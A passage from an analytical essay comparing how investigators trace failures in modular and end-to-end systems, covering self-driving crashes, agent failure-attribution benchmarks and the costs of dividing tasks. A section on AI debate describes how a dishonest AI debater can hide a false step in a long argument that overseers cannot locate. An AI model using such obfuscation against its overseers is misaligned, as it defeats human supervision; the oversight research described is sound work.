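| 2.5 | Bicycle | Along the next lane |
| 1.5 | Unknown object | Stationary, partly in the car's lane |
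| 1.2 | Bicycle | In the car's lane |

Uber's self-driving car first detected the pedestrian from about 107 metres away. At 44 mph it could have stopped in a little over 40 metres, even within the company's limits on hard braking. But the software did not predict a collision until 1.2 seconds before impact.

The software normally used an object's past positions to predict where it was heading. Whenever the object's classification changed, the software discarded those positions and treated the object as stationary. If the classification then held for a moment, the software assumed that a vehicle or bicycle would continue along its lane. Someone crossing at walking pace moves about four metres sideways in three seconds, which was a full lane on this road, so the discarded positions would have shown that she was crossing. The software could predict that a pedestrian would cross away from a crosswalk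 only after classifying the person as a pedestrian for long enough to measure their movement, and it never classified her as a pedestrian.

Braking failed for other reasons. When the software detected an emergency, it held back the brakes for one second while it rechecked the hazard, without alerting the operator. Uber had added this delay to prevent violent braking after false alarms. After that second, the car would brake hard only if it could still avoid the collision completely. In Tempe it could not, so it sounded an alert and planned a gradual slowdown 0.2 seconds before hitting the woman at 39 mph.

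The NTSB's figures allow a rough estimate of the delay's effect. Uber limited how hard the software could brake (7 m/s²) and how quickly the braking could build up (5 m/s³). If the car had started braking as hard as those limits allowed when it recognised the emergency, about 22 metres from the woman, it would have reached her at about 35 mph. With the quicker build-up of 20 m/s³ that Uber adopted later, it would have reached her at about 23 mph. Removing the delay would have achieved little unless Uber had also raised the build-up limit, which would have had almost no effect by itself.

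The NTSB could use the records to describe these rules and the order in which they took effect, but the records do not show why the perception software kept changing its classification. No module reported a fault during the trip. The modules mostly did what their designers had specified, and the dangerous behaviour came from how the rules worked together.

Uber later tested its repairs by running the sensor data from the crash through newer software. According to NTSB's *Vehicle Automation Report*, the company said the new version would have recognised a pedestrian from about 88 metres and started braking more than four seconds before the original impact. The new version kept an object's past positions when its classification changed and no longer delayed emergency braking. It also included other changes, so the test does not show how much each repair contributed.

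### Causes outside the software

NTSB identified the operator's inattention as the probable cause. She was streaming a television show on her phone and looked down for about five of the last six seconds before the crash. NTSB concluded that an attentive operator would probably have had time to avoid the crash or make it less severe.

The contributing causes included Uber's weak risk assessment, its poor supervision of operators and Arizona's insufficient oversight of testing. Uber had switched off the Volvo's own emergency braking during automated driving, partly because the car's radar and Uber's could interfere with each other. The company had also cut the number of people in each test car from two to one. Its cars had driven the route about 50,000 times, and operators had occasionally encountered people crossing outside crosswalks.

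None of these causes appeared in the messages between modules. The NTSB recommended safety assessments, reviews of applications to test on public roads, and a proper safety management system at Uber, but none of its six recommendations was to change a particular module.

In *Death By Uber 4*, Green accepts NTSB's account of how supervisors lose vigilance but finds it inexplicable that NTSB named the operator as the probable cause and Uber as a contributing one. She had completed the route 72 times without trouble, and he argues that a loss of attention was inevitable. More detailed software logs could not settle this disagreement, because it is about what Uber could reasonably expect of a human operator.

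### A crash with several possible repairs

On 2 October 2023, a hit-and-run driver in San Francisco struck a pedestrian and threw her into the path of a robotaxi run by Cruise, a subsidiary of General Motors. The robotaxi hit her at 18.6 mph, according to Smart Cities Dive, and stopped. It then pulled over at up to 7.7 mph, dragging her about 20 feet.

Cruise hired the engineering firm Exponent to find the technical cause. Axios' *Cruise "deeply remorseful" after scathing report on robotaxi pedestrian incident* (2024) reports that the car had correctly detected, classified and tracked both the pedestrian and the other vehicle before the collision. The car then misclassified the impact as a side collision and, as a result, pulled over when it should have stayed where it was.

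The car had also lost track of the woman. After the impact, most of her body was outside the lidar's view (Carrier Management, 2024). Her feet and lower legs remained visible to a side camera until the car finally stopped. Electrek (2024) reports that the software briefly detected them but did not classify or track them.

An engineer could therefore name several repairs that might have prevented the dragging. Perception could have kept track of the legs, the collision software could have identified the impact as frontal, or the planner could have kept the car stopped after a person it was tracking disappeared at the moment of a collision. Koopman (2024) proposes making the car wait for remote confirmation before it moves after hitting a pedestrian. This would have worked without better perception, and it would also cover cases where the car loses track of someone for other reasons.

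The investigation also had gaps that module logs could not fill. Investigators could not establish exactly what Cruise's remote assistance team saw that evening (Fortune, 2024). Cruise's crash report left out the dragging, and Bauranov (2026), in *Crash Course for Robotaxis*, treats this omission as a second failure. More than 100 employees knew the full facts before the company met officials the next day, according to Electrek. The published findings are divided between a 109-page report by lawyers, much of it about who knew what and who told whom, and a redacted 86-page technical analysis (Koopman, 2024).

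### When the first repair does not hold

Waymo's trouble with school buses shows why a diagnosis needs testing after the repair. In autumn 2025, its cars in Austin, Texas, repeatedly passed school buses that had stopped with their red lights flashing. Waymo updated its software in November and in December filed a recall covering about 3,000 vehicles.

Austin's school district reported further violations after Waymo's first fix, and the NTSB opened an investigation in January 2026. Waymo's engineers may have correctly repaired a real fault in one module but left other causes in place. A car can pass a stopped bus because, for example, it fails to see the lights, misjudges which lanes must stop, or decides too early that the bus has finished.

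Cameras on the district's buses recorded the cars going past, so the district could tell that the problem continued without seeing Waymo's logs. Readable modules can help engineers choose a repair, but engineers can learn whether it was enough only from how the car behaves afterwards. In a system like Waymo's, where the modules are trained jointly, repairing one module can also change how neighbouring modules behave, so engineers have to test the whole car again.

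### Investigating an end-to-end car

If the car in Tempe had run on a single network, investigators could still have established most of what the NTSB concluded. They would have had the sensor recordings, the car's speed, the video of the operator and her phone records. They could have found out that Uber had disabled the Volvo's automatic emergency braking and removed the second operator. If the one-second delay had been written in ordinary code that ran after the network, they could have seen it as easily as they did in the modular car.

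Engineers could also have run the network on edited versions of the recording. If it failed to brake for the woman with the bicycle but braked when they removed the bicycle, that would show that the bicycle affected the decision. They could repeat the test in daylight, at a crosswalk or with a slower walker to find the conditions in which the car failed. Elluswamy described Tesla using replays in a similar way.

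In an end-to-end network, an investigator would have much more difficulty finding the equivalent of the rule that discarded past positions, because the same weakness might be spread over millions of parameters. A readout might display "vehicle", "unknown object" and "bicycle" in turn, but the braking might not depend on those labels. In the modular car, engineers could change one rule and know that the software would keep past positions in every later scene. With the network, they would have to retrain on similar crossings and then check a wide range of scenes to see how far the improvement extended.

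Modular logs therefore made it clearly easier to explain and repair the software. They mattered less to the conclusions about the operator, the company and the state, which the NTSB ranked as the main causes.

### Reading an agent's log

Language-model agents leave logs in ordinary text, which might make it easier to trace a failure to its source. In *Which Agent Causes Task Failures and When?*, Zhang, Yin and colleagues (2025) built the first benchmark for this task, Who&When. It contains 184 failures from 127 systems of cooperating agents, on questions that required work such as web research and reading files. Three experts marked the agent and step responsible for each failure.

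The experts spent about 84 hours on this, or 27 minutes per failure. They often had to visit the websites an agent had used to find out whether the information was missing or the agent had overlooked it. Each expert was unsure of between 15% and 30% of their own labels.

Zhang and colleagues then asked language models to do the same job. They gave a model the whole log at once, showed it the log one step at a time, or had it repeatedly choose which half of the log contained the error. The best accuracy was 53.5% for naming the responsible agent but only 14.2% for naming the exact step.

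Failures were hard to trace partly because the logs recorded what each agent wrote but not what it had received. Suppose a worker wrongly reports that no payment matches line 40 of the ledger. The planner may have left the payment out of the worker's input, or the worker may have overlooked it, and the worker's message would be the same in both cases. *Seeing the Whole Elephant* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) estimated that developers could not reliably attribute at least 21% of the Who&When failures from outputs alone.

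The TraceElephant benchmark contains 220 failures, with the full input to every step. It also includes metadata (the agents' instructions and tools, and the system's design) and the software needed to rerun each case. The table shows how often a language model found the component and step that experts had identified as the source of the failure.

| What the model could use | Right component | Right step |
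|---|---|---|
| Outputs only | 54% | 17% |
| Outputs and metadata | 56% | 19% |
| Outputs, metadata and inputs | 65.9% | 30.3% |
| All of these, with the ability to rerun steps | 66.7% | 33.3% |

In these tests, the model also had the correct answer to the task. Without it, the scores in the last row fell to 60.6% and 27.6%. Developers usually have the correct answer when they debug on test problems, but a company may not have it when its agent misreports the company's accounts.

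The inputs made the biggest difference, and they are easy to record because ordinary code assembles the context for each call. A developer who saves only the messages between agents loses much of the diagnostic value of a modular design. Even with everything available, the model chose the wrong step two times out of three.

Mistakes near the start of a run were especially hard to find. In Magentic-One, a system with a fixed team of agents, the model located 52% of the decisive steps in the last third of the log but only 8% of those in the first third. An early error is often a bad plan, which may look reasonable until later agents have built on it. A supervisor would most like to catch these errors, since correcting them early saves the most work.

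TraceElephant allows a rough comparison between teams of agents and a single agent. SWE-Agent, which repairs software, uses one agent whose scaffold has separate functions for planning and using tools. With full logs, the model found the right component in 63.6% of SWE-Agent's failures and the right step in 29.6%. For the two multi-agent systems, the figures were about 67% and 31%. The systems did different tasks and SWE-Agent contributed only 44 failures, so small differences are weak evidence. But the results give no sign that dividing work among several agents made failures much easier to trace when the single agent also left a full log.

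### Better methods in 2026

Attribution methods improved quickly over the following months. In August, *ASCon* (Jiang, Ran and colleagues, 2026) presented a small model that learns from annotated failures. It represents a log as a network of steps and agents, keeping what came before each step separate from what came after. On 790 test cases from the same collection as its training data, it found the right agent 81.0% of the time and the right step 63.3% of the time.

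Those scores did not carry over to unfamiliar systems. On Who&When, without further training, the model identified the agent responsible in only 45.7% of failures and the step responsible in 20.1%. Its predictions were more useful as input to a large language model. When Jiang and colleagues gave them to DeepSeek-V4-Pro, that model's accuracy on steps rose from 22.3% to 43.5%. A company that runs the same agents every day could train a specialised tool on its own failures, but the tool would probably work less well after a major redesign.

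*Error-Propagation Modeling for Failure Attribution in LLM-Based Multi-Agent Systems* (Liao, Zhai and colleagues, October 2026) reported better results on Who&When without training on it. Its method, EMFA, traces backwards from the visible failure through the steps that supplied information to it. It separately looks for loops in which agents repeat the same action without progress. Together these searches produce up to four candidate errors, and a language model judges whether correcting each one would have prevented the failure.

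EMFA found the right step in 32.8% of the failures from the hand-built team and 50.0% of those from automatically generated teams. Over all 184 failures, it found the right step in about 45% and the right agent in about 69%. The base model was GPT-4o, so the improvement over the 2025 results came largely from a better method, and current frontier models might do better still.

Some of the improvement may come from the explicit principles Liao and colleagues gave EMFA for assigning responsibility as the experts do, for example when one agent writes a faulty plan and another carries it out. These principles are useful to a developer who agrees with them, but they also mean that the score partly measures agreement with a convention.

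### More than one correct answer

The conventions differ between the two benchmarks. Zhang and colleagues call an error decisive if correcting it would have turned the failed run into a success:

run fails as it happened, and run succeeds with step t corrected.

If several errors meet this test, they choose the earliest. Chen and colleagues choose the earliest step after which failure was inevitable. If a later module was supposed to catch the error, the run was still recoverable, so they blame that module for missing it.

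Suppose a worker copies a payment of 1,450 as 1,540 at step 3, and the verifier approves it at step 5. The first rule blames the worker and the second blames the verifier. Correcting either step would have made the report accurate, so nothing else in the log can settle which module was at fault.

The NTSB's finding on Tempe resembles Chen and colleagues' rule. Uber expected the operator to catch the software's errors, and she was the last person who could have prevented the crash. Green's objection to the finding also applies to the rule. If the verifier is the same language model as the worker and tends to miss the same mistakes, blaming the verifier for missing one places too little blame on the designer.

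Two independent errors cause a different problem. Suppose one worker misreads payment 17 and another misreads payment 40, and either mistake alone would make the total wrong. If an investigator corrects one and leaves the rest of the run unchanged, the total is still wrong, so neither error is decisive. Zhang and colleagues avoid this by assuming that the later steps are also corrected. Under that assumption, the earlier mistake gets the blame because it came first.

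Language models add a further complication because the same step can turn out differently on each run. A verifier that missed the wrong payment once might catch it the next time. Investigators could then measure how much a correction changes the chance of success:

effect of step t = P(success with step t corrected) − P(success when rerun unchanged).

Suppose the unchanged run succeeds 20% of the time, correcting the worker raises this to 90%, and correcting the verifier raises it to 85%. The effects are 70 and 65 points, which add up to more than 100, so they can't be shares of the blame. A developer can still conclude that either repair would help. Rerunning a system many times takes a lot of compute, and it is impossible if the agent has already sent the payment.

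Disagreement among experts is consistent with these difficulties. In TraceElephant, experts first labelled the failures independently. Their agreement was 0.72 on the component and 0.64 on the step, where 0 is chance agreement and 1 is perfect agreement. They then discussed the uncertain cases and settled on one answer for each. A method that gives a different answer is counted as wrong, even if an expert initially gave the same answer.

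Sometimes the fault lies between modules. Albayaydh, Zhao and Flechais (2026), in *Beyond the Leaderboard*, summarise a taxonomy by Cemri and colleagues that divides 14 kinds of multi-agent failure into three groups: problems with the specification, misalignment between agents and failures of verification. For example, one worker agent might list payments with sales tax included while another lists invoices without it. If the planner agent never said which to use, both workers have followed their instructions, but their lists don't match. A benchmark that assigns each failure to one agent would probably assign this one to the planner, but the developer who wrote the planner's instructions may be better placed to fix it.

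Developers rarely need to identify a single cause to fix a failure. They can list the changes that would have prevented it and choose the one that is easiest to make or prevents the most other failures, as Koopman did in his proposal for the Cruise car. Identifying a single cause matters more for legal liability, or when an automatic system decides which module to retrain. In those cases, people have to agree beforehand what each module is responsible for.

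### When no step looks wrong

All these methods assume that an investigator who reaches the faulty step can recognise it. *Debate update: Obfuscated arguments problem* (2020), by Beth Barnes and Paul Christiano, describes arguments for which this assumption fails. It concerns debate, a proposed way of supervising AI in which two AI systems argue for opposite answers and a person judges. The debaters divide a claim into smaller ones until the judge can check one directly. If a claim is false, the honest debater should be able to lead the judge to the mistake.

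Barnes and Christiano found that a dishonest debater could construct a long argument in which neither debater could identify the wrong step, even though the honest debater knew the conclusion was false. They called this the obfuscated arguments problem.

Suppose, for example, that someone claims a 600-digit number is prime and divides the argument into 1,000 subclaims, each stating that the number has no factor in a certain range. An expert can use a quick test to prove that the number is not prime, but the test doesn't reveal its factors. At least one subclaim must then be false, but finding it could take longer than anyone can wait. If only one is false, checking ten at random gives a 1% chance of finding it.

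Questioning the person who made the argument might not help, because they may not know where the factor is either. The same could happen with an agent's long forecast or policy analysis. A reviewer might have good independent reasons to reject the conclusion but still find each of the hundreds of steps plausible.

Jonah Brown-Cohen, Geoffrey Irving and Georgios Piliouras proposed a reply in *Avoiding Obfuscation with Prover-Estimator Debate* (2025). One AI system, the prover, divides its claim into subclaims. The other, the estimator, gives each subclaim a probability and doesn't have to identify the false one. For the 600-digit number, the estimator could give each range a 99.9% chance of containing no factor and still reject the conclusion, because it expects one of the 1,000 ranges to contain a factor.

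The prover must then argue that one of the estimated probabilities is too high or too low, and the debate continues on a disputed subclaim. A prover who doesn't know where the flaw is has no advantage over the estimator in this challenge. Brown-Cohen and colleagues proved that, under certain assumptions, an honest debater can win with about as much computing power as its opponent. Under the earlier rules, the honest debater might have had to solve a problem that no realistic computer could.

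The most important assumption is stability, meaning that the conclusion must not depend on very small changes in the probabilities of the steps. This makes some true claims harder to defend. If a number is prime but the prover's only argument is the list of 1,000 ranges, a doubt of 0.1% about each range is enough to undermine the argument. The prover would need a more stable argument, such as a short proof of primality that the judge can check directly.

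## What does decomposition cost in capability?

Dividing a job among modules gives investigators more to examine after a failure, but it can also cause failures. A module may leave something important out of its message, or misread a message from another module. Studies of language-model agents report effects on performance ranging from a 70% loss to an 81% gain. The effect depends mainly on the task, how much information is lost in each handoff, and the strength of the single agent used for comparison.

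### Why a message can't add information

Tran and Kiela (2026), in *Single-Agent LLMs Outperform Multi-Agent Systems on Multi-Hop Reasoning*, make the theoretical case for a single agent. Let Y be the correct answer, C everything the single agent can read, and M a message that another agent writes after reading C. The mutual information I(Y; C) measures how much knowing C reduces uncertainty about Y. The information that C and M together give about Y can be split in two ways:

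I(Y; C, M) = I(Y; C) + I(Y; M | C) = I(Y; M) + I(Y; C | M).

The writer had only C to work from, so M adds nothing for a reader who already has C, and I(Y; M | C) = 0. The last term, I(Y; C | M), can't be negative. It follows that

I(Y; C) ≥ I(Y; M).

This result is called the data processing inequality. Anyone who could explain an account shortfall from a worker's note on the bank statement and ledger could also explain it from those two documents, because they could write the same note themselves.

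The inequality favours a single agent in practice only if three conditions hold. The team's budget, which Tran and Kiela measure in thinking tokens (the text a model produces while reasoning), must be no larger than the single agent's. The single agent must make perfect use of its context, however long it is. Finally, C must include everything the team knows. If a worker queries a database that the single agent never consults, the worker's message can contain information missing from C.

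Tran and Kiela tested four models on two sets of questions that require combining several facts. The table shows accuracy averaged over all eight combinations of model and question set.

| Design | 1,000 thinking tokens | 10,000 thinking tokens |
|---|---|---|
| Single agent | 41.8% | 42.6% |
| Planner divides the question into steps, done in order | 37.9% | 38.7% |
| Planner divides the question into parts, done in parallel | 36.9% | 39.9% |
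| Agents with different roles, each given the whole question | 38.1% | 42.3% |
| Two agents answer, then criticise each other | 38.8% | 42.0% |
| Several agents answer and a judge picks one | 33.3% | 42.0% |

With the larger budget, the three designs that give every agent the whole question scored within a point of the single agent. The two that divide the question stayed three to four points behind. Using several agents therefore lowered scores only slightly, and most of the remaining loss came with dividing the question, which also gives a reviewer intermediate results to read. With only 100 tokens, the single agent did worse than most of the teams, but no design had enough tokens for useful reasoning.

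Some of the loss is visible in the models' reasoning. On 1,175 of the harder questions, Gemini 2.5 Flash answered 124 correctly only when working as a single agent and 72 only when working as a step-by-step team. In 23 of those 124, the team's reasoning contained the right answer but its final answer did not.

Tran and Kiela also weakened the second condition by corrupting the context. When they replaced 30% of its tokens with random ones, the single agent still performed better, but at 70% the step-by-step team was clearly better. Adding irrelevant sentences on a related topic, which is closer to what happens in a long agent run, reduced the single agent's advantage but didn't reverse it.

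### The cost of a long context and the cost of a handoff

Anchan and Sen model what happens when an agent's accuracy falls as its context fills up. They give each step a loss, −ln(probability of success), so that adding losses is the same as multiplying probabilities. In their ledger example, the loss at a step with c tokens of context is

g(c) = 0.002 + 0.000005 · c.

The agent starts with 1,000 tokens of instructions, and every transaction adds 400. Over 20 transactions, a single agent's total loss is

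20 × 0.002 + 0.000005 × (20 × 1,000 + 400 × 210) = 0.56,

where 210 is the sum of the numbers from 1 to 20. The chance of getting every step right is e^(−0.56), or 57%.

Now suppose four agents handle five transactions each. The first has a loss of 0.065. Each of the others also reads a 300-token summary, which raises its loss to 0.0725, and adds a handoff cost h for whatever the summary left out. The total is

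0.065 + 3 × (0.0725 + h).

If each handoff has about a 2% chance of spoiling the job (h = 0.02), the team succeeds 71% of the time. If h is 0.10, it succeeds 56% of the time, slightly less often than the single agent. The two designs succeed equally often when h is about 0.09.

The same formulas give the results for other ways of dividing the 20 transactions.

| Division of the work | Success, handoff cost 0.02 | Success, handoff cost 0.10 |
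|---|---|---|
| One agent | 57% | 57% |
| Two agents, ten transactions each | 67% | 62% |
| Four agents, five each | 71% | 56% |
| Twenty agents, one each | 56% | 12% |

The best number of steps per agent is roughly √(2h / λk), where h is the loss per handoff, λ is the extra loss per token and k is the number of tokens added per step. This is about 4.5 steps when the handoff loss is low and 10 when it is high. A single agent does much worse on longer jobs. With 100 transactions and a handoff loss of 0.02, it would succeed about once in 50,000 attempts, while twenty five-step agents would succeed 16% of the time. If accuracy didn't depend on context length at all, λ would be zero and dividing the work could not beat using a single agent, which is Tran and Kiela's conclusion.

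Anchan and Sen chose these numbers to be plausible, then measured real ones using gpt-oss-20b, a small open model. In their test ledgers, some transactions referred to earlier ones only by an ID, so the agent had to find the amount in its context or in a handoff note. The single agent got 2.7% of steps wrong when its context was below 2,000 tokens and 71% when it was above 36,000. The penalty for a handoff note was about 0.036. From these measurements, they calculated that five-step agents should start to outperform the single agent at about ten transactions.

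| Transactions in the ledger | One agent's final balance correct | Five-step agents' final balance correct |
|---|---|---|
| 20 | 49% | 64% |
| 50 | 4% | 18% |
| 100 | 0% | 10% |

The team outperformed the single agent at all three ledger lengths. On a related measure that leaves out percentage fees, the predicted success rates were within nine points of the observed ones. On the shortest ledgers, the team produced twice as many tokens as the single agent, mostly in its notes. On the longest, it produced about the same number but read a tenth as much input, because the single agent had to reread its whole history at every step.

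This is good evidence that division can help, but weak evidence for exactly where the crossover falls. All three lengths tested were well above the predicted crossover of ten transactions, and Anchan and Sen settled on their method of analysis after the runs were complete. The estimated loss from handoffs was also very uncertain, with a 95% interval from −0.10 to 0.18.

The steep drop in accuracy also depends on the task. In a separate test, the same model did arithmetic about as well after 63,000 tokens of irrelevant text as after none. But about a quarter of its responses left out the answer line requested in the instructions, which came before the irrelevant text. Although the number was usually still right, a scaffold that searches for that line would record a failure. Repeating the instruction next to the question might be a simpler fix than adding agents.

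Models that handle long contexts better need fewer handoffs. Consistent with this, Anthropic's developers could remove the short writing stages from their scaffold when they moved to a stronger model.

### Tasks that divide and tasks that don't

*Towards a Science of Scaling Agent Systems* (Kim, Gu and colleagues, 2025) makes the broadest comparison, with nine models and six kinds of task. It compares a single agent with four types of team: agents that work independently, agents under a central coordinator, agents that debate each other, and a mixture of coordination and debate. The table shows changes relative to the single agent's score.

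| Task | Single agent's score | Best team | Worst team |
|---|---|---|---|
| Financial analysis | 34.9% | +81% | +57% |
| Web research | 31.8% | +9% | −35% |
| Office tasks | 62.9% | +6% | −11% |
| Command-line tasks | 34.4% | +2% | −19% |
| Repairing software | 52.2% | −2% | −15% |
| Planning in Minecraft | 56.8% | −39% | −70% |

In financial analysis, one agent could read regulatory news while another searched company filings and a third assessed operations. The coordinator then combined their findings, and the average score rose from 34.9% to 63.1%. In Minecraft, by contrast, a single agent can craft an item in three moves: look up the recipe, place the materials and craft. The team gave one agent the recipe and another the inventory, which every agent could already see, so only the third agent did necessary work. Sending messages also used effort the agents needed for planning.

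Some of the gain in finance may come from extra computation. Kim and colleagues gave teams and single agents the same maximum number of steps, but estimate that teams needed 1.6 to 6.2 times as many tokens to reach the same performance.

Kim and colleagues also report that independent agents amplify errors 17.2 times, compared with 4.4 times for agents under a central coordinator. These figures, estimated from the tokens in execution records, measure the extra work that coordination failures cause, not the number of wrong answers. The teams failed tasks only about 1.1 to 1.3 times as often as the single agent. Once they accounted for other features of the teams, such as efficiency, Kim and colleagues found that error amplification did not significantly predict performance. A coordinator that checks results before combining them is still a sensible design, but the 17.2 figure greatly overstates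 what a company would lose without one.

Adding agents tended to lower performance on tasks that a single agent completed more than about 45% of the time. The statistical model behind this threshold explained only 37% of the variation in scores on held-out data, though it correctly predicted the best design for 87% of held-out configurations. The strongest models in the study date from 2025. Newer models can complete more of these tasks alone, which probably leaves fewer cases where adding agents helps.

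### Combining what different agents know

Agents in the ledger test pass information along a chain, but agents may also have to combine data that is split among them. *SILO-BENCH* (Liu, Yang and colleagues, 2026) split the input to each of 30 programming-style problems among 2 to 100 agents, then compared the teams with a single agent that had all the data. With gpt-oss-120b, teams of two lost 15% to 49% of the single agent's success rate. Teams of 50 lost 80% to 100% of it on the harder problems, such as sorting a list split among the agents.

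Liu and colleagues conclude that agents gather the information they need but fail to combine it. On the easiest problems, DeepSeek-V3.1 scored 88% when near misses earned credit, but only 62% of its answers were exactly right. The gap shows that many agents came close, but a near miss could result from missing data as well as from a failure to combine it. The test is also harsher than most scaffolds because it requires every agent to give the complete answer, whereas a company needs only one correct report.

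To look more closely at how pairs of agents fail, Sun, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *The Collaboration Tax*, designed 32 puzzles that a model can usually solve alone and split the information for each between two agents. The weakest of the 11 models succeeded about half as often in pairs as alone, and stronger models lost less. In failed conversations, agents more often stated facts that neither had been given, didn't ask for what they lacked, didn't write down the combined information, or accepted an answer without recalculating it.

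Adding four instructions to the prompt, one for each of these mistakes, recovered about 38% of the loss. Two of the instructions, which require agents to list the facts from both sides before answering and to show their recalculation, would also leave a record in the conversation that a reviewer can check.

Comparisons with a weak single agent can hide these losses. A common stronger baseline is self-consistency, in which one model answers the same question several times and its most common answer is used. In *PACE*, Sajjadi Mohammadabadi (2026) audited nine studies and found that of 123 teams that beat a single attempt, 53 did not beat repeated sampling. Against sampled or budget-matched baselines, teams were 4.2 points less accurate on average. The audit includes results from Tran and Kiela and from Kim and colleagues, so it doesn't independently confirm them.

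### Handing over everything the next step needs

The largest gain from dividing work comes from a system that people designed for one task. In *The Illusion of Multi-Agent Advantage*, Jwalapuram, Lin and colleagues (2026) built a set of problems in which a model must use long tables of share prices to find which investor first or last reaches a given profit or loss. GPT-5 solved 57.0% of them with self-consistency and 96.5% with the expert-designed system. Anchan and Sen estimate that the system cost about 16% more than the baseline. One of its modules turns the question into a structured form. For each investor, a second module extracts the relevant prices and a third does the calculation. Ordinary code runs these modules and compares the results.

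Systems that design their own teams did much worse. The largest significant improvement was 6.6 points, for a weaker model, at five times the cost. Jwalapuram and colleagues found that the agents in such systems often did redundant work. In one system, agents based on GPT-5 agreed immediately more than 90% of the time, so the system did little more than take a vote, at high cost.

The expert-designed system's result shows what a good division can achieve, but not how often developers will find one. The same researchers created the problems and the system, and they built the problems to suit a team. The gain also combines the effects of shorter contexts and of letting code make the final comparison. The model still has to be good enough at each part. GPT-4o improved only from 22.1% to 22.6% because it kept making mistakes in retrieval and arithmetic.

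An even finer division worked on the Towers of Hanoi, a puzzle in which a player moves a stack of disks between pegs without placing a larger disk on a smaller one. Anchan and Sen describe how Meyerson and colleagues solved a version with about a million moves and no errors. Each call to the model chose a single move, and the scaffold repeated the call until one move led the others by a set number of votes.

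Voting can make individual errors extremely rare. Suppose each call is wrong 1% of the time, the errors are independent, and all wrong calls choose the same move. The chance that the wrong move wins is then

1 / (1 + 99^k).

With k = 3, the chance of a wrong move after voting is about one in a million, so a run of a million moves would succeed only about 36% of the time. With k = 4, the chance is about one in 96 million, and the run would succeed 99% of the time. But if the model made the same mistake on every call for even one position in 100,000, voting would not correct those mistakes, and a million moves would contain about ten errors.

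The handoffs must be nearly perfect too. Over a million steps, a 0.00001 chance of failure at each handoff would limit the chance of success to e^(−10), or about 0.005%. Meyerson and colleagues avoided this by passing on the complete position of the disks instead of a summary. A short list holds everything that matters in the puzzle, and a program can check whether each move is legal.

When a message contains everything the next module needs, the system loses little capability in the handoff, and a reviewer gets a more complete record. To hand over parts of an account, an agent may need to pass on only the current balance, the open items and references to their source records. A forecast or an investigation of possible fraud is harder to hand over, because an agent can't easily tell which of its observations will matter later.

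### Modules that depend on their neighbours

A module's value depends on the modules around it. In *AgentSpec*, Chen, Shen and colleagues (2026) built agents from interchangeable modules for memory, reasoning and reflection, then tested them on tasks such as running deliveries in a simulated city. Replacing a simple memory with one called MemoryBank raised one agent's hourly profit from 8.54 to 30.67. The same change raised profit from 6.18 to 26.78 for an agent with a different reasoning module, while a third agent, which used plain chain of thought, had smaller and inconsistent gains. Developers could replace the memory without rewriting anything else, but they had to test the whole agent to learn how much the replacement helped.

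Chen and colleagues also found that models trained by reinforcement learning work best in a scaffold when developers train them with that scaffold. A company that cares about performance therefore has a reason to train its modules together, or at least to train each one around the others. Doing so would bring back the pressures that cause leakage and language drift. To get the best performance from its modular agent, the company might have to make the messages between modules a less reliable record.

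### What the readable list costs a planner

In a car, a list of objects serves as the handoff note. Two results described earlier roughly indicate how much capability is lost, but they measure different things. UniTeD performed better when it learned perception and planning together, which suggests that training modules separately reduces performance. PARA-Drive's planner had more collisions when it received boxes instead of vectors, which shows the harm from making one particular list its only information about the scene.

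The PARA-Drive figures come from open-loop tests. In a closed-loop test, the car acts on each plan, so small mistakes can grow or the planner can correct them. The gap between boxes and vectors could therefore be larger or smaller there. The gap would also depend on how much the list describes.

Companies' safety records would not answer the question either, because Waymo's cars use lidar and radar as well as cameras, Tesla's network drives from video, and the companies operate in different places. To measure how much the interface reduces capability, researchers would need to give the same sensors and training data to a planner that takes a list as input and one that takes vectors, then test both on the same routes.

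### Dividing for performance or for inspection

Most of these studies measure what happens when developers divide a task to improve performance. Those developers can put boundaries wherever accuracy is highest and remove any that don't help. A developer who divides a task for inspection needs boundaries where a person can check something, such as after each match between a payment and an invoice, and these may not be the best places for performance.

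In the ledger example, with a handoff cost of 0.02, the best result in the table is 71% success, with five transactions per agent. If a reviewer wanted more checkpoints and insisted on a separate agent for every transaction, success would fall to 56%. The drop would be much larger with a handoff cost of 0.10.

However, a reviewer can get a note after every transaction without a handoff. The same agent can write the note using a few extra tokens and continue with its full context, so its next step can still draw on information that isn't in the note. Capability therefore falls little when a reviewer only reads the agent's results, and falls more when the next step must depend only on what the reviewer has read.

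A few experiments come closer to measuring how much capability is lost in exchange for that guarantee. Radhakrishnan and colleagues' model lost about four points of accuracy when it used separate contexts, and a concept model lost at most 1.3 points when its values were rounded, provided its list of concepts covered the task well. Neither experiment measured how many more mistakes a human reviewer caught as a result. A company deciding whether to accept a 15-point drop in its agent's success rate would need that number, because a less accurate agent could still produce better accounts if reviewers caught and corrected enough of its errors.

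## Oversight that does not require reading the modules

People can keep some control over an agent without reading anything that passes between its parts. They can add an independent checker that can reject the agent's proposed actions before the agent takes them, whatever reasoning produced them. They can also measure how the whole agent behaves and use the results to decide whether to let it run. Both methods work on a single network as well as on a set of modules.

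### A formula for a safe gap

Mobileye's Responsibility-Sensitive Safety (RSS) is a set of driving rules that a program can apply to any planned trajectory. Shalev-Shwartz, Shammah and Shashua (2017), in *On a Formal Model of Safe and Scalable Self-driving Cars*, turn five common-sense rules, such as not hitting anyone from behind, into formulas. The rules are meant to ensure that the car never causes a crash. They can't guarantee that it will never be in one, because a car surrounded by traffic on a motorway can't stop the others from hitting it.

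To avoid hitting the car ahead, the car behind must leave room for a bad case. The car ahead brakes hard, and the car behind speeds up until it reacts, then brakes only moderately. The smallest safe gap is

gap = v·ρ + ½·a·ρ² + (v + a·ρ)² / 2b − u² / 2B,

or zero if the result is negative. Here v is the speed of the car behind and u the speed of the car ahead. The response time is ρ, and a is the most the car behind might accelerate during it. After that, the car behind brakes at b or harder, while the car ahead never brakes harder than B.

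As an illustration, let both cars travel at 20 metres per second (about 45 mph), with ρ = 0.5 seconds, a = 2 m/s², b = 4 m/s² and B = 8 m/s². Then

gap = 10 + 0.25 + 55.1 − 25 = 40.4 metres,

or about two seconds of driving. If a planner proposes closing to 30 metres at this speed, the checker can reject the trajectory. If the gap becomes too small anyway, the car must start braking at 4 m/s² or harder within half a second.

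Shalev-Shwartz and colleagues prove that a car that always responds this way never hits the car ahead if their assumptions hold. *Slow Down, Move Over* (2023) confirmed the result for motion along the lane using a theorem prover, a program that checks each step of a proof. But if the car ahead brakes at 10 m/s², it stops in 20 metres instead of 25. A car that left the minimum gap and reacted as slowly as the rule permits would then hit it.

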